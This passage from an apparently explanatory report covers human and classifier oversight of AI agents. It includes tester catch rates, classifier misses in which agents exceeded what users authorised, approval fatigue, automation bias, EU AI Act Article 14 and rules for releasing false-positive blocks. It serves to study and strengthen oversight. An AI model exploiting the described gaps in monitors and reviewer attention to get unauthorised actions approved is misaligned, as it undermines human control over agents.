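| Testers, whole study | 13.6% |
| Testers, early in a session | About 17% |
| Testers, after at least 50 prompts | About 5% |
| Auto mode's classifier, same commands | 89% |

The prompts became less effective with repetition, but most testers approved the dangerous command even early in a session. The testers caught only six of the 116 commands that the classifier let through, so asking people like them to review what the classifier allows would add little protection. Their catch rate was also below the level of about 20 per cent that made asking a person worthwhile in the earlier payment example.

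Users protecting their own files may be more careful than paid testers with nothing to lose. Anthropic also published these figures to justify making auto mode the default. In its earlier, less favourable tests, the classifier missed 17 per cent of 52 real cases in which an agent had gone beyond what the user authorised. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but wrongly classified the action as authorised. For example, a request to "clean up" a code change does not authorise the agent to overwrite the project's history. Anthropic still recommends careful human review for high-stakes infrastructure.

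*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analysed 290 reports of agents damaging files and found that user review had contributed to 105 of them. In 80 cases, the users had set the agent to run without prompts, often because they would otherwise have had to answer hundreds of them. In 31, the prompt gave the user too little information. A request to run `python3 setup.py`, for instance, looks routine, but the script could do anything. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, warns that repeated approvals may come from habit, fatigue or a need to keep working, rather than from growing trust. Software that learns from past approvals could therefore learn to permit actions that nobody had considered.

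People do heed some warnings, such as the browser warnings mentioned earlier, probably partly because those are rare. A payment agent should therefore ask only about actions with serious consequences. Chrome's agent, for example, asks before signing in with a saved password, according to Parker. The question should also describe the action's effect, and *Let the Agent Do It?* suggests showing whether the user could undo the action.

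People can also decide before the task begins. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026) studies rules that people without a software background write in plain language about spending, sending, deleting and access to private information. A clerk could decide once that the agent must never pay a new account without permission, instead of having to notice one in the fortieth prompt of the day.

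A security verdict in the prompt can also lead to automation bias, the tendency to accept an automated system's output without enough checking. Parasuraman and Manzey reviewed the research in *Complacency and Bias in Human Use of Automation* (2010) and concluded that this bias affects experts as well as novices, and that training or instructions do not prevent it. A clerk who reads "no known finding" beside a payment may therefore look less closely at the account number. "Link checked; account number not checked" would at least show the clerk what still needs checking.

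### What the EU AI Act requires

Article 14 of the EU AI Act requires providers to design high-risk AI systems so that people can oversee them effectively while they are in use. These people must be able to understand the system's limits, interpret its output correctly, disregard or reverse that output, stop the system, and remain aware of automation bias. The article does not generally require a person to approve each action, but for remote biometric identification, two people must usually confirm a match separately before anyone acts on it.

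High-risk uses include screening job applicants and assessing people's creditworthiness. An agent that only pays supplier invoices would probably not fall under the article. For an agent that does, an approval button may not be enough if the person pressing it has neither the time nor the information to refuse.

The Act originally set 2 August 2026 as the date from which these duties apply to high-risk systems in listed areas such as employment and credit. The Digital Omnibus, a package of amendments that the European Commission proposed in November 2025, postpones this to 2 December 2027 at the latest. It sets a latest date of 2 August 2028 for AI built into regulated products such as medical devices.

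### Releasing a false positive

Whichever check has the final say will sometimes block legitimate work. In Anthropic's test on 10,000 real tool calls, auto mode's classifier needlessly blocked 0.4 per cent. If such errors were independent, about 27 per cent of tasks with 80 calls would contain at least one. The user doesn't need to review most of these blocks, because the agent usually finds another acceptable way to continue. After three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, Claude Code hands the decision to the user, or stops if the agent is running unattended.

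When no acceptable alternative exists, somebody needs the authority to allow the action. In Microsoft's Azure SRE Agent, only users with the administrator role for the agent can grant it temporary permissions. Other users can read the request but can't act on it. Administrators can't grant more than their own permissions allow, and the result shows who gave the authorisation.

Claude Code gives users more freedom. They can approve a command once or save a rule that applies to all future sessions in the same project, but approvals for editing files end with the session. Auto mode is designed never to approve certain actions, such as sending secrets to an outside service. A user who wants to take such an action has to leave auto mode or run the command themselves.

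An accounts office could set its own rules for releases along these lines:

| Blocked action | Who may release it | How long the release lasts |
|---|---|---|
| Reading a page on an unrated domain | The clerk | One visit |
| Opening a page on a phishing list | The security team, after examining it | One day, followed by a new check |
| Installing a flagged skill | The security team | Until the skill's files change |
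| Paying an unfamiliar account | A manager who did not request the payment and has phoned the supplier | One payment of the stated amount |

A permanent exception for the supplier's domain would be risky, because attackers could later take over the site. The release should cancel only the mistaken finding. If the security team decides that a phishing list flagged the supplier in error, the firm's other checks on the payment should still apply.

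The record of a release has to be detailed enough for someone to judge the decision afterwards. Mehta and Agarwal say that for every action with serious consequences, a platform should be able to identify who asked for it, what it did, what it affected, what data it carried, what evidence supported it and whose authority it used. For a release, the firm should add the original finding, the reason for overruling it and the expiry time. Software outside the agent's control should write this record and copy the evidence directly from the tools. Mythos 5's invalid arguments about the maintainer show why an agent's own explanation is not enough.

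An administrator can also use these records to find faulty rules. If staff release nearly everything that one check blocks, the check may be too strict, in which case the firm should adjust it or report the error to its vendor. But staff may instead be approving releases out of habit. To find out which, a second person could re-examine a sample of the released actions without knowing that they were released.
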